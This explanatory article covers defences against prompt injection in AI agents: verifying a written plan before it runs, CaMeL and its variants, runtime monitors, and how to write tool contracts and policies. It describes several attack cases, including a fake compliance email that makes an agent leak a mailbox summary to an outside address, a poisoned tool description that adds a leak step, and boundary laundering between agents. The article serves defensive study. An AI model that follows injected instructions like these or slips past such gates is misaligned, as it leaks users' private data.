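# Checking AI-written code for unsafe tool calls before it runs

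## Why a tool call should be checked before it runs

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that carries out the model's requests. Each request, such as sending an email or deleting a file, is a tool call. Most agents make one tool call at a time and wait for its result before choosing the next. In another design, the model first writes all the calls a task needs as a small program, called the plan. A separate component, called the gate, then checks the plan against machine-readable rules, called the policy, before any call runs. Programming language designers have checked untrusted programs this way since the 1990s. In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), Erik Meijer, one of these designers, proposed doing the same for agents.

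His main example is an agent with two tools, one for fetching email and one for sending it. A user named Michelle asks it to fetch and summarize her emails. Four are ordinary business messages about a seed round, a conference invitation, new securities rules, and a follow-up on an investment. Another, posing as a compliance notice, says that all mailbox contents need an external backup. It instructs the assistant to send a summary to an outside address as its next action, without asking the user or mentioning the message afterwards. The agent sends the summary, then writes Michelle a correct digest of the four ordinary emails, with no sign of the leak.

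Reading the agent's answer would not have helped her. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), an account of Meijer's later conference talk, notes that an agent can empty a bank account and then return an acceptable sentence. The check should therefore be on the actions that lead up to the answer.

### The agent loop and prompt injection

The attack works because an ordinary agent loop puts all its text into one input. The application first sends the model the developer's instructions, descriptions of the tools and the user's request. The model returns either an answer or a structured request that names a tool and its arguments. If it requests a tool, application code performs the call, appends the result to the input and runs the model again, repeating this until the model returns an answer. On the second pass, the input contains both Michelle's request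 and the attacker's email, and the model chooses its next call based on all of it.

A prompt injection is text placed in material that a model reads, which the model then follows as an instruction. An attacker can plant this text in an email, a web page, a tool's response or the tool description supplied to the model.

Meijer traces the problem to a missing distinction between code and data, and compares it with SQL injection, an old attack on databases. If a website pastes a visitor's input directly into a database command, an attacker can type a fragment that ends the intended command and adds another, such as one that deletes the table of users. The standard fix is a parameterised query, in which the program sends the database a command with blanks in it and sends the values for the blanks separately. SQL's grammar distinguishes commands from values, so the database can never execute a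 value, whatever it contains.

A language model's input has no grammar that separates instructions from data, as David C argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. A model only predicts the next token from the text so far, and labels such as "instruction" and "data" are more text. Training a model to prioritise its instructions, or marking outside content as data, makes an attack harder but doesn't rule it out. David C thinks it quite possible that prompt injection will never be fixed the way parameterised queries fixed SQL injection. He would rather treat the model as a "confusable deputy", a component that an outsider can trick into using its privileges on the outsider's behalf. On this view, the designer should assume the worst case, in which the attacker has direct access to every tool the model can call, and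 limit the damage with deterministic safeguards that do not rely on a language model.

Meijer's remedy puts the boundary between instructions and data outside the model by having the model write its plan before it sees any emails. The model therefore doesn't have to tell the two apart, which makes the disagreement narrower than it looks. The emails come in later as the values of named variables, like the values that fill the blanks in a SQL query, after the list of tool calls is fixed. The SQL comparison holds fairly well within the plan, but it fails again wherever a tool itself calls a model. A summarizing tool that reads a malicious email could still produce a distorted summary, though it could not add a call that sends mail. The model also reads the user's request and the tool descriptions before it writes the plan, so a poisoned description can still influence the plan.

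### When the usual defences act

A tool call should be checked before it runs because some actions, such as sending an email, can't be undone. The simplest defence is to log everything the agent does and have a security team read the logs, which may help to catch the next attack but can't reverse a call that has already run.

Asking the user to approve each call can stop an unsafe call before it runs, but only if the user reads the prompt. Meijer expects people to tire of these prompts and click "Allow", and recent figures support this. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users of the company's coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. They reject 39% of the plans that the agent presents for approval, which may mean that they read a whole plan more closely than a single command, or just that they wanted something else done. In an experiment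 with 1,053 paid testers, the organizers swapped one prompt per session for a plainly dangerous command, and only 143 testers (13.6%) stopped it. The rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more prompts. An automatic classifier blocked 937 of the same commands. Anthropic published these numbers to justify replacing the prompts with the classifier, and the testers had less reason to be careful than real users because they weren't working on their own projects, but the gap between the testers and the classifier is still very large.

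A runtime monitor checks each tool call just before it runs, without asking the user. One kind is a small state machine that follows the agent's calls and moves to an error state when, say, a message is addressed to an outside domain. Another is Anthropic's classifier, a second model that evaluates each call. According to *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tools' results or the agent's own prose, which keeps injected text and the agent's rationalizations away from it. On 10,000 real tool calls by employees, it blocked 0.4% of the harmless ones. On a set of 52 real actions in which the agent had gone beyond what the user authorized, it let through 17%.

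Monitored agents now do well against prompt injection in particular. In a July 2026 evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, none of 720 attempts succeeded against Anthropic's newest models with the classifier on. The models themselves seem to account for most of this result, since the average success rate was only 0.09% with no safeguards. Attempts against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19.03% of the time when it had full access and 5.83% of the time with OpenAI's own automatic reviewer. The attacks had been tuned on an older Anthropic model, so the evaluation is weak evidence of how well the current models would resist attacks tuned on them.

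These results show that monitors can stop some unsafe actions, so the argument for checking earlier has to rest on something else. Meijer argues that in the email case a monitor acts too late even if it blocks the outgoing message, because the agent has by then retrieved and processed private mail. This argument seems weak, because Michelle asked the agent to read her mail, and blocking the message to the outside address prevents the leak.

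The argument is much stronger for tasks with several effects. When a monitor denies the second side effect, the first may already have happened. The documentation for clauz3, a tool that checks agent-written Python programs, calls this an awkward failure for transactional programs (*Background And Related Work*). Suppose an airline's agent cancels a booking and then requests a refund, and the monitor blocks the refund because the amount did not come from the reservation record. The monitor has enforced its rule correctly, but the customer has neither a seat nor the money. A gate that checked both steps together beforehand would have rejected the plan before the booking was cancelled. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou and Eckhoff, 2026) also argues for checking a plan in advance because a rejected plan leaves no changes to undo.

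Blocking single actions also does little to get the task done safely. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, reports one experiment on tau-bench, a benchmark in which an agent handles customer-service requests under a company's written rules. Monitors blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. This is a single study, and Dantas and colleagues ask for a replication. But the underlying limitation is more general, because a monitor can't evaluate actions the model has not yet generated and so can't detect whether the call it is about to allow leads to a dead end.

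### Generate, verify, execute

In "generate, then execute", the model writes the plan before any data arrives, which stops the email in Michelle's inbox from adding a call. It doesn't stop a malicious tool description. Meijer's example is a mail-fetching tool whose description claims that, for compliance reasons, the agent must also send summaries of all emails to a certain address. A model that follows this description will write the leak into the plan. A malicious user could also ask for the same step.

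The extra stage in "generate, verify, then execute" therefore checks the plan before it runs. The policy in this example forbids any data from the fetching tool's result from flowing into the body of an outgoing message, unless the recipient belongs to the company's domain. The gate searches the plan for such a flow, for instance with CodeQL, a tool that turns a program into a database that can be queried for patterns. The poisoned plan contains such a flow, so the gate rejects the plan and no email goes out. For rules about arguments and effects, such as which files a deletion may touch, Meijer suggests Z3, a solver for logical formulas, or Dafny, a language with a built-in program verifier.

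The AI Engineer talk describes two separate requirements. First, a component other than the model must execute the model's plan, because otherwise there is no point at which anyone could refuse it. Second, the plan must be a data structure that a checker can traverse, because delaying a computation helps little if nobody can inspect it.

In a toy plan language, a plan can finish with an answer, read a file and continue, or remove a file and continue. The rules for proving that a plan deletes nothing cover finishing and reading but not removal. A model can still write a plan that removes a file, but no proof exists for that plan, so the component that executes plans rejects it. For a plan that reads a file, the proof has to cover every text the file might contain, so the component can accept or reject the plan before anyone opens the file.

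Checking "during generation" can mean two things. It mainly means that the gate examines a finished plan before the plan has any effect. It can also mean checking partial code as the model writes it, perhaps line by line, and halting or steering the model once a fragment breaks a rule. Partial checking can catch some errors sooner, but it relies on less information. *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) includes an airline rule that requires an agent to confirm, before cancelling a reservation, that the passenger has not flown any part of it. If a fragment cancels a reservation without that check, no later code can repair the error. But a fragment that fetches private mail does not show where the mail will go.

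### Bytecode verification and proof-carrying code

Meijer presents the pattern as an extension of what Java and .NET do with bytecode, the compact instructions that their virtual machines run. Early web browsers with Java support downloaded bytecode from strangers, with no guarantee that a trustworthy compiler had produced it. Yellin's *Low Level Security in Java* describes how the verifier checks this bytecode. For every instruction, it records what types of value the memory slots would hold just before that instruction runs. It works out how the instruction changes those types, passes the result to every instruction that could come next, and merges the records where two paths meet. It repeats this until the records stop changing. Code passes only if every instruction receives values of the right type on every path that could reach it.

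Two features of that design carry over to agents. First, some checks still happen at run time. The verifier postpones certain lookups until the code needs them, and Meijer adds that Java and .NET test array indexes during execution. Second, the verifier is, in Yellin's words, "extremely conservative", and rejects some programs that a more sophisticated prover might certify.

The other precursor is proof-carrying code, which George Necula set out in *Proof-Carrying Code* in 1997. It leaves the hard part to the producer of the code. The party that will run the code (the consumer) publishes a safety policy. A mechanical procedure turns the program and the policy into a logical formula, the verification condition, whose truth guarantees that the program obeys the policy. The producer finds a proof of the formula and ships it with the program. The consumer computes the formula again, checks that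 the proof establishes it, and can then run the code many times without further checks. Finding the proof may be slow and need human help, but checking it is quick. If an attacker alters the program, it either fails the check or is still safe. The consumer has to trust only the small proof checker and its own policy, not the producer.

An agent fits the role of untrusted producer well, but not exactly. Meijer writes of agents that generate proofs, yet in his worked examples no proof accompanies the plan, and the gate does the analysis itself. clauz3 also proves each program afresh with Z3, with carried proofs left to future work. Anyone who builds such a gate must therefore trust more than Necula's consumer did, because a whole solver or analysis engine has to be correct, along with the code that translates plans into its input.

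The tools must also behave as the gate assumes. A tool contract specifies what must be true before a call, what will be true afterwards and what the call leaves unchanged. These contracts make up much of the checker's model of the tools. A checker is sound if, given that model, it never accepts a plan that breaks the policy. In the toy example, the proof that a plan deletes nothing can't be relied on if the component that reads files also secretly deletes them. The proof doesn't cover confidentiality either, because the rule doesn't include it.

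Soundness alone is also easy to achieve, since a gate that rejects every plan is sound. The hard part is limiting false alarms, which are rejections of plans that obey the policy. Researchers therefore measure how many tasks an agent still completes as well as how many violations get through. The tau-bench family of benchmarks suits rules about procedure, such as the airline's. AgentDojo is a common choice for prompt injection. In it, an agent attempts email, banking, travel and chat tasks both with and without planted instructions.

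## Writing the whole plan before any data is read

To keep instructions apart from data, the agent's designer controls what the planning model reads and when. The model writes the whole plan from only the user's request and the tool descriptions. A step often needs the result of an earlier one, such as the emails that a fetching tool will return. That result doesn't exist yet, so the model writes a name for it, called a symbolic reference. Once the plan is complete, a separate program called the interpreter runs the steps and replaces the names with real values, without showing those values to the planning model.

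### A plan for Michelle's emails

In Meijer's example, the model answers Michelle's request with a plan in JSON, a text format for nested data. Each step that calls a tool has a description, the tool's name, its arguments, a name for the result and the name of the next step. Without the descriptions, the plan amounts to three lines:

```
emails_fetched = fetch_mail()
email_summary  = summarize_emails(emails_fetched)
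return email_summary
```

The interpreter calls the fetching tool and stores the results, including the fake compliance notice, as `emails_fetched`. It passes the stored emails to the summarizing tool, stores the output as `email_summary` and returns it to Michelle. The notice contains an instruction to send a message to an outside address, but the interpreter takes its steps only from the plan, and the plan has no step that sends mail. The planning model could have added one, but it finished before the interpreter fetched the notice and doesn't run again.

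The summarizing tool does run a model on the notice. Meijer suggests telling this model to mark dubious messages, and in his sample output it labels the notice as suspicious. If the model misses a dubious message, Michelle gets a distorted summary, but no mail goes out.

All of this depends on the interpreter treating stored values only as data. If it pasted the text of the emails into the plan and parsed the result again, an attacker could write an email that closes one step and opens another, as in SQL injection. Meijer's published JSON also has a smaller ambiguity, because the reference `emails_fetched` and the file pattern `*.txt` in his file-deletion example are both ordinary quoted strings. An interpreter needs a rule for telling references from literal strings, and the safest is probably to give references their own type.

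### What each plan format makes checkable

A JSON syntax tree, in which every part of the plan is a labelled node, is the easiest format to check. Each call and argument is explicit, so a checker can trace the emails by following their name from step to step. In Meijer's example, each step leads to only one next step. But many tasks need choices ("if the fare is under $300, book it") or repetition ("for each unpaid bill"), and a format that allows these gives the checker more paths to examine.

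Restricted Python has both, and models already write Python well. The subset in CaMeL, a system described below, leaves out arbitrary `while` loops and uncontrolled `break` statements, which according to Nikolaou and Eckhoff would make it harder to work out the possible orders of calls from the text. Python still offers many ways to write the same thing. A plan can pass a recipient by position or by name, and can nest one tool call inside another's arguments, so a checker has to reduce these variants to one form before it applies a policy. clauz3 accepts more ordinary Python and executes it symbolically, running the program on unknown values and recording the conditions under which each call would happen.

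In his 2026 talk, Meijer chose a more abstract format, using Lean, a programming language that also checks mathematical proofs. AI Engineer explains that a checker can't inspect computations in `IO`, Lean's own type for computations with side effects, so the model returns a description of the computation instead. A description is either a finished answer or one operation, such as reading a file, together with a function that takes the operation's result and returns the rest of the description. Functional programmers call this structure a free monad. Building one performs no operations. The interpreter later carries out the first operation, gives the result to the function, and repeats this with the description that the function returns.

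The function lets the rest of the plan depend on what the file contains, which the straight-line JSON example can't do. It also makes the plan harder to check by simple traversal, since the later steps appear only when someone supplies the contents. The proof attached to the plan solves this problem because it has to cover every possible file content. The model writes the proof and Lean checks it. Few users could read such a plan, but Meijer doesn't mind, because machines write, check and run it. The plan loses one advantage of his earlier version, in which he translated the JSON steps into plain English so that users could follow them.

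The open-source implementation of the 2025 article, metareflection/guardians, stays closer to JSON. normalform-ai's *Guardians Synergies*, a design note that compares guardians with clauz3, describes guardians' plans as syntax trees in which a placeholder, `SymRef`, stands for a future result. This presumably removes the ambiguity between references and literal strings. The operator describes each tool in a `ToolSpec` and writes the rules in a `Policy`. The rules can forbid flows from a source to a sink, restrict the order of calls with a state machine, or set conditions that must hold before and after a call, which Z3 checks. At the end of his 2026 talk, Meijer pointed to an implementation by Nada Amin of Harvard and other academics, probably this one. AI Engineer notes that it doesn't use free monads.

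guardians and clauz3 also differ in who writes the rules. A guardians operator sets the policy, whereas clauz3's agent proposes a contract for its own program and asks the user to consent to it. normalform-ai suggests translating guardians plans into the same list of effects that clauz3 extracts from Python, so that one prover could check both, but this is still only a proposal. The note also leaves open whether planning before reading suits coding agents at all. A coding agent usually has to read the code before it can know what to change.

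### CaMeL

CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning) is the best-known system that writes its whole plan before reading any data. Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues published it in March 2025 in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. It builds on Simon Willison's 2023 "dual LLM" pattern, which divides the agent's work between a privileged model and a quarantined model.

Suppose a user asks the agent to find Bob's email address in a chat channel and tell him that a meeting starts at 3pm. The privileged model reads this request and writes a short program in restricted Python. The program fetches the channel's messages, asks the quarantined model to extract Bob's address from them, and emails the meeting time to that address. CaMeL's interpreter then runs the program and makes the tool calls. The quarantined model reads the untrusted messages, but it has no tools and must return its answer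 in a form that the program specifies, such as a single email address. An instruction hidden in the channel can therefore change which address the program uses, but it can't add a tool call.

The attacker may only want to change the address. To counter this, CaMeL attaches labels, called capabilities, to every value to record its sources and permitted readers. The interpreter also tracks which values the program computed from which others, so Bob's address still counts as coming from the channel. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a Python function that checks the call, its arguments and their labels, then allows or denies the call. One policy lets the agent change a password only if the new password came from the user. Another could stop the agent from emailing a calendar entry to someone who is not among its permitted readers.

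CaMeL applies these policies at runtime, one call at a time, as a fixed plan runs, so it can still stop a task halfway through. It does this at runtime because some labels depend on facts that are unknown during planning, such as who wrote the description of a calendar event. CaMeLoT adds a check before the plan runs for the rules that can be settled by then.

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarizes the original results as showing that CaMeL eliminated nearly all of AgentDojo's attacks at comparable task performance. In later tests, CaMeL again stopped nearly all attacks but reduced task completion more than in the original results. For *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues reran CaMeL with five models on AgentDojo's 97 tasks and on 949 attack cases per model. They divided the tools among several agents, each running CaMeL.

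| Model | Tasks completed without CaMeL | Tasks completed with CaMeL | Attacks succeeding without CaMeL | Attacks succeeding with CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 91.1% | 84.4% | 1.5% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 73.2% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 78.4% | 38.1% | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3% | 42.3% | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 27.8% | 13.4% | 2.1% | 0.0% |

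Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, perhaps because they resemble attacks, so its completion rates cover only the other 45. The experimenters switched off CaMeL's policies, so the lost tasks come from fixing the plan in advance and not from denied calls. Ilia Shumailov, one of CaMeL's designers, took part in the study, so hostility to the system is unlikely to explain the losses.

CaMeL removes a serious weakness in GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro but greatly lowers their scores. It lowers GPT-5.5's score by 13 points and prevents no attack in the benchmark. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that the 0% attack success rate doesn't show immunity, since the attacks were fixed in advance and adaptive attackers in large contests have found successful attacks on every frontier model they tried. For the newest models, the main reason to use CaMeL is therefore its guarantee against attacks outside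 the benchmark.

Two other groups also found substantial losses. In *ToolFence*, Li, Cao and Xiao (2026) ran CaMeL on AgentDojo with Qwen3-max. Attack success fell from 21.2% to 0%, and completion of harmless tasks fell from 66.3% to 43.1%. CaMeL's runtime overhead was 12.95× on the subset they timed. ToolFence is a competing defence, so these figures may not show CaMeL at its best. Nikolaou and Eckhoff ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5, with the policies on and no attacks, and it completed 49 of the 97 tasks. On 22 tasks the plan ran but didn't do what the user wanted, and the policies blocked at least 17 more.

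### What the separation leaves open

The planning model still reads the tool descriptions, so an attacker who writes one can add a step to the plan. Li and colleagues tested this with MCPTox, a benchmark of malicious instructions in tool descriptions. With Qwen3-max, 38.1% of the attacks succeeded with no defence and 12.3% succeeded against CaMeL. Part of that drop may come from plans that crashed, because the experimenters counted an execution error as a failed task but not as a successful attack. ToolFence brought the rate down to 6.1%. It keeps two lists of tools, and the component that issues permissions reads only the list the host has reviewed, not the third-party descriptions. A planner could follow the same rule, as long as someone reviews each tool before the agent uses it.

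Planning early gives no protection against a malicious request, because the planner is meant to carry out the request. Only the policy can help in that case. A request can be malicious even when the user isn't, because when one agent calls another, the first agent's message becomes the second agent's request. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL on GPT-5.2, and planted an instruction in a database of job applicants. They then asked the system to send Julie a summary of some of the applicants on Slack. The database agent and the coordinating agent both kept to their plans, but the coordinating agent pasted the summary, including the planted instruction, into its message to the notification agent. That agent's planner treated the message as a trusted request and added a step that emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

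The researchers call this boundary laundering, and it accounts for every attack that succeeded against CaMeL in their benchmark. Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each message between agents into an instruction and a set of named values. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the receiving planner sees the values' names but not their contents. No attack in the benchmark succeeded against multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5's completion rate fell further, from 73.2% to 66.0%, while Fable 5's stayed the same on the tasks it didn't refuse.

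An attacker can also corrupt a value inside a correct call, as with Bob's address. A policy that accepts only recipients named by the user would block a forged address, but also Bob's real one, because both came from the channel. Labels show only where a value came from, not whether it is right. ToolFence allows a more specific rule. If the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a particular file, the recipient must appear in what the agent read from that file. An account number from a stray email would then fail the check, but a forged one in the file itself would still pass.

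Untrusted data can also influence a fixed plan in subtler ways. If the plan contains an "if" that depends on an email, the sender can affect which branch runs, though not what the branches contain. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this branch steering. They also relay two criticisms of CaMeL by Garby, Gordon and Sands. The first is that the interpreter misses some dependencies that pass through an "if". Suppose a plan sets `approved` to true and changes it to false only if an email contains the word "cancel". When the word is missing, the change never runs, and `approved` can keep its trusted label even though its value depends on the email. The second is that CaMeL retries after a failure, and a series of failures can leak some private data because whether a policy denies a call can depend on that data.

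### When the next step depends on what is read

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark that adapts its attacks to each defence, sorts requests by how much the user leaves open. In "pay Bob $50", the user specifies both the action and its details. In "pay the bill in this file", the user names the action but leaves the details to the file, and symbolic references handle this case well. In "do what the email asks", the user doesn't name an action. Attacks succeeded much more often on this last kind of request, which is also the kind that a planner can't plan for without reading the email.

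Suppose Michelle says, "Do what the conference organizers' email asks." The email might ask her to confirm that she is coming, pay a fee or send a short biography. One option is for the planner to write a branch for each case:

```
email = fetch_mail(sender = "organizers")
kind  = classify(email, ["confirm", "pay", "biography", "other"])
if kind == "confirm":    reply(email, "Michelle will attend.")
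if kind == "pay":        pay(saved_payee, amount_in(email))
if kind == "biography":  reply(email, saved_biography)
if kind == "other":      show_to_user(email)
```

`classify` is a quarantined model that can return only one of four words. The gate can check all four branches before anything runs, which keeps the main benefit of planning first. An attacker who controls the email can still choose the branch and the amount, so every branch has to be acceptable for any email. In this plan the payee comes from Michelle's saved contacts, and the policy should also cap the amount. The main drawback is that the planner must guess the cases in advance. Three such choices in a row give 64 paths, and any unforeseen case goes to the user.

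Another option is to run the planner again after it has read the email. The planner can then handle any request, but it has read text that an attacker may have written, so the policy becomes the only barrier. The gate also can't check the whole task at once, because it approves the first plan before the second is written. A designer can limit the damage by allowing only reads in the first plan and checking the whole second plan before it changes anything. A stricter version shows the planner only the label that `classify` returned, not the email. A choice among four labels carries at most two bits of information, which leaves an attacker very little room to write instructions. This works like branching in advance, except that the planner writes only the branch it needs.

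ToolFence replans one call at a time. If the agent proposes a call that its original permissions don't cover, a separate model reviews the call and its exact arguments. If the reviewer approves, ToolFence adds a permission for that call, and the agent has to propose it again. In Li and colleagues' tests on AgentDojo with Qwen3-max, the agent completed 64.3% of harmless tasks with ToolFence, close to the 66.3% it completed with no defense, and no attack succeeded. But the reviewer is a model and can make mistakes. On AgentLAB, a benchmark whose attacks unfold over many steps, 29.4% of attacks succeeded against ToolFence, compared with 35.2% against CaMeL.

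*PlanGuard* (Gong and Deng, 2026) lets the agent read everything and act as usual, but compares each call with a reference plan that a second planner writes from only the request and the tool definitions. Requiring an exact match blocked 27% of harmless cases in one half of the benchmark and 38% in the other, often because of trivial differences such as "last_week" and "lastweek". When a model judged the mismatched arguments instead, these rates fell to about 1% and 3%, and still no attack succeeded. However, that model reads the agent's reasoning, which an email containing injected instructions may have influenced. PlanGuard also always blocks tools that are missing from the reference plan, so the agent could not carry out a request like "do what the email asks" unless the second planner happened to guess the right tool.

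The remaining option is to ask Michelle, since only she knows whether she meant to authorize a payment when she told the agent to follow the email. The question should show the tool, recipient and amount taken directly from the plan, because an attacker could influence a summary that a model writes after reading the email. She should be asked once about the whole second plan, not once for each call. Claude Code's users reject plans far more often than single permission prompts, so they may read plans more carefully. Asking makes most sense for payments, deletions and messages to outsiders, while branches can handle the routine cases.

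### The effect on task success

In 2025, Meijer wrote that nobody had formally measured how planning first affects an agent's success, though he saw strong signs that "thinking in code" improves reasoning and reliability. Later CaMeL results suggest the opposite, at least for plans the model must write without seeing any data. Peters-Gill and colleagues also tested CaMeL on 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark for industrial equipment maintenance. Completion fell by an average of 21.6 points across the five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest.

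They conclude that stronger models handle the constraint better. This seems true overall, but there are exceptions. GPT-5.5 lost only 5.4 points on AssetOpsBench, whereas Fable 5 lost 21.4, more than the much older GPT-4.1 did.

They report that most of the failures came from committing to a plan before seeing the data. Sometimes a result showed that the task needed another call, and the plan had no branch for it. In other cases an agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for something similar, and the rest of the plan ran unchanged. The planner also has to write code to parse a tool's output before seeing any. Neither benchmark documented what its tools return, so the experimenters had to add a description of the output format to every tool, as anyone who builds a system of this kind will have to do.

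In most of these failures, a good enough planner could probably have written a working plan. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) counts only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks as impossible to plan in advance, yet GPT-4.1 lost about 39 tasks under CaMeL. Better models and better documentation should recover many of these. They can't do much for tasks whose next action is unknowable until the agent has read something. All 60 of AgentDyn's own tasks, which cover shopping, software repositories and daily life, are of this kind, and defences that depend on an initial plan, including CaMeL, completed far fewer of them. Before choosing this design, it is worth counting how many of an agent's real tasks are like this.

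*Do LLM Agents Execute the Plans They Declare?* (2026) supports having separate software carry out the plan. Agents that declared a plan and then acted step by step kept to its structure in only 22–45% of runs. Software that enforced the declared structure raised success from 48% to 92% on ALFWorld, a set of simulated household tasks, and from 36% to 44% on SWE-bench Verified, a set of software bugs. The experiment is weaker evidence for writing the plan before reading any data, because the models could choose among several kinds of plan, including a search, which presumably responds to results along the way.

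## Writing the rules and describing the tools

Before a gate can check any plan, someone has to write a policy and describe each tool in a contract. Without a contract for `send_email`, the gate has only the tool's name and no record that the call delivers text to another person.

### Tool contracts and kinds of rule

For Michelle's agent, short contracts might look like this:

```
fetch_mail()
    returns:  private mailbox data
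    changes:  nothing
summarize_emails(emails)
    returns:  text derived from emails
    changes:  nothing
send_email(to, body)
    requires: every entry in to is a valid address
    effect:   everyone in to receives body
    changes:  nothing else
```

The "changes" lines are frame conditions, which matter most for tools that delete or overwrite things. The contract for `summarize_emails` is the easiest to leave out because summarizing looks harmless. Without it, a checker that treats a tool's output as unrelated to its input stops tracking the emails at that step and misses any leak through the summary. A cautious checker assumes that the output of a tool without a contract depends on its input.

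Some policy rules limit the arguments of a single call, such as the size of a refund. A data-flow rule prohibits any flow of data from a named source to a named sink. A sequence rule requires or forbids a particular order of calls, like the airline rule that the agent must check for flown segments before canceling a reservation.

A rule can be written as a prohibition or a precondition, and the choice matters when a fact is missing. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) define the two in *NOMOS*, a compiler that turns written company policies into rules for tool calls. A prohibition blocks a call while its condition holds, so the call goes through if the relevant fact is missing. A precondition blocks a call until its condition holds, so a missing fact stops the call. The compiler therefore defaults to preconditions for rules about confirmation or authorization.

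### From an office rule to a formal one

"Mailbox contents must not leave the company" is clear enough for a new employee, but to turn it into a formal rule, someone has to decide what each part covers.

"Mailbox contents" identifies the source, which is the result of `fetch_mail`. A summary of the emails reveals much of what they contain, so the rule also has to cover everything computed from that result. If the agent later gets a tool for searching mail or opening attachments, that tool's results are another source.

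The word "leave" determines the sinks. The obvious one is the body of an outgoing email, but a subject line, an attachment, a web request or a calendar invitation can carry the same text. Returning the summary to Michelle doesn't count as leaving. The summarizing tool is a harder case because it may send the emails to a model that another company hosts. Most offices would probably allow this, but someone should decide it explicitly.

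"The company" has to be defined in terms a program can test, most simply by the domain of the recipient's address, which is valleysharks.com in Meijer's example. This definition is imperfect, since an internal mailing list can have outside members and the company's lawyer may have an outside address.

"Must not" allows no exceptions, so Michelle couldn't ask the agent to forward a conference invitation to a friend. The operator can accept this loss, or allow an outside recipient whom Michelle names herself. On the strict reading, the rule becomes:

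```
For every possible run of the plan,
and every call send_email(to, body) in that run:
    if body depends on any result of fetch_mail,
    then every address in to has exactly the domain valleysharks.com.
```

"Every possible run" covers plans with branches, and "every address" covers a message sent to both a colleague and an outsider. If the plan takes the recipient from an email, the gate can't determine the domain before the plan runs. It must then either treat the recipient as an outsider and reject the plan, or leave that one domain comparison to a runtime monitor.

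Small choices in how a policy is interpreted can change results a great deal. The airline policy in τ²-bench, the successor to tau-bench, requires the user's confirmation before a change, but it leaves unclear whether one "yes" can cover several changes announced together. Yu and colleagues found that an unprotected agent broke the encoded rules in 66.3% of its state-changing calls if each change needed its own "yes", and in 36.8% if one "yes" covered the batch.

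### Two errors in Meijer's rule

Meijer gives a formal version of the same office rule. Condensed, it reads:

```
source: fetch_email, result email_summary
sink:   send_email, argument body,
        if to is not in *.valleysharks.com
```

The rule names the wrong source. In the article's JSON plan, the tool is `functions.fetch_mail` and its result is `emails_fetched`, while `email_summary` is the output of the summarizing tool. A checker that matches names would find no source in such a plan, and therefore no forbidden flow, so it would accept a plan that mails the summary to an attacker. The mistake is easy to miss because the article's plain-English version of the poisoned plan does use the name `fetch_email`.

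The recipient pattern is also wrong. Read as an ordinary wildcard, `*.valleysharks.com` matches any text followed by `.valleysharks.com`. The address `michelle@valleysharks.com` has an @ sign where the pattern requires a dot, so it doesn't match, and the rule treats Michelle as an outsider.

Meijer presents the rule only as an example of a possible policy. The rule as printed also isn't valid JSON, so a strict parser would fail to load it. This is the least dangerous of the three mistakes because the operator would notice it immediately.

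The other two can hide each other, as four test plans show:

| Plan | Correct verdict | Meijer's rule | With only the source corrected |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch, summarize, send to an outside address | Reject | Accept | Reject |
| Fetch, summarize, send to michelle@valleysharks.com | Accept | Accept | Reject |
| Fetch, summarize, return the summary to Michelle | Accept | Accept | Accept |
| Send a greeting without mailbox contents to an outside address | Accept | Accept | Accept |

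Testing the leaking plan reveals the wrong source in the rule. Testing the internal email reveals the wrong pattern, but only after someone has corrected the source, because until then the rule never applies. An operator who tested only harmless plans would see the published rule pass every time, so it is worth checking that each rule rejects at least one test plan.

Deleting the dot from the pattern makes things worse. The new pattern, `*valleysharks.com`, matches Michelle's address but also `eve@notvalleysharks.com`, so anyone who registers that domain can receive the company's mail. `*@valleysharks.com` excludes that address, but if the tool accepts several recipients in one string, the pattern also matches `eve@example.org, bob@valleysharks.com`. The rule should split the recipients, extract each domain and check that it is exactly `valleysharks.com`. The test set should include each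 of these addresses.

A simpler check catches the wrong source without a test plan. When the gate loads a policy, it can compare every tool name in it with the list of installed tools and refuse a policy that mentions `fetch_email` when no such tool exists. This wouldn't help if the operator later added a second mail-reading tool and forgot to list it as a source. A stricter form of the rule handles both cases by allowing an outgoing message to contain only fixed text and results from tools the operator has marked as public. A misspelled or forgotten tool then causes a false alarm instead of a leak, and a false alarm is much easier to notice.

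### How many requirements can become rules

The office rule at least has a formal version. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 80 benchmarks for the safety and security of agents and found that 68 of them (85%) state no requirement that anyone could verify. Of these, 49 give the agent no policy and 19 give only goals, such as refusing "anything unsafe" without defining it. Seven of the 80 have verifiable rules, and five were unclear.

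These figures describe research benchmarks, and companies may write better policies than benchmark designers do. Still, the vagueness causes trouble. Hong and colleagues tried to reconstruct the missing rules from the benchmarks' scoring but gave up, partly because the scores conflicted. One customer-relations benchmark has a task where the agent should refuse to judge whether a sales lead is qualified, and another where it should answer an almost identical question.

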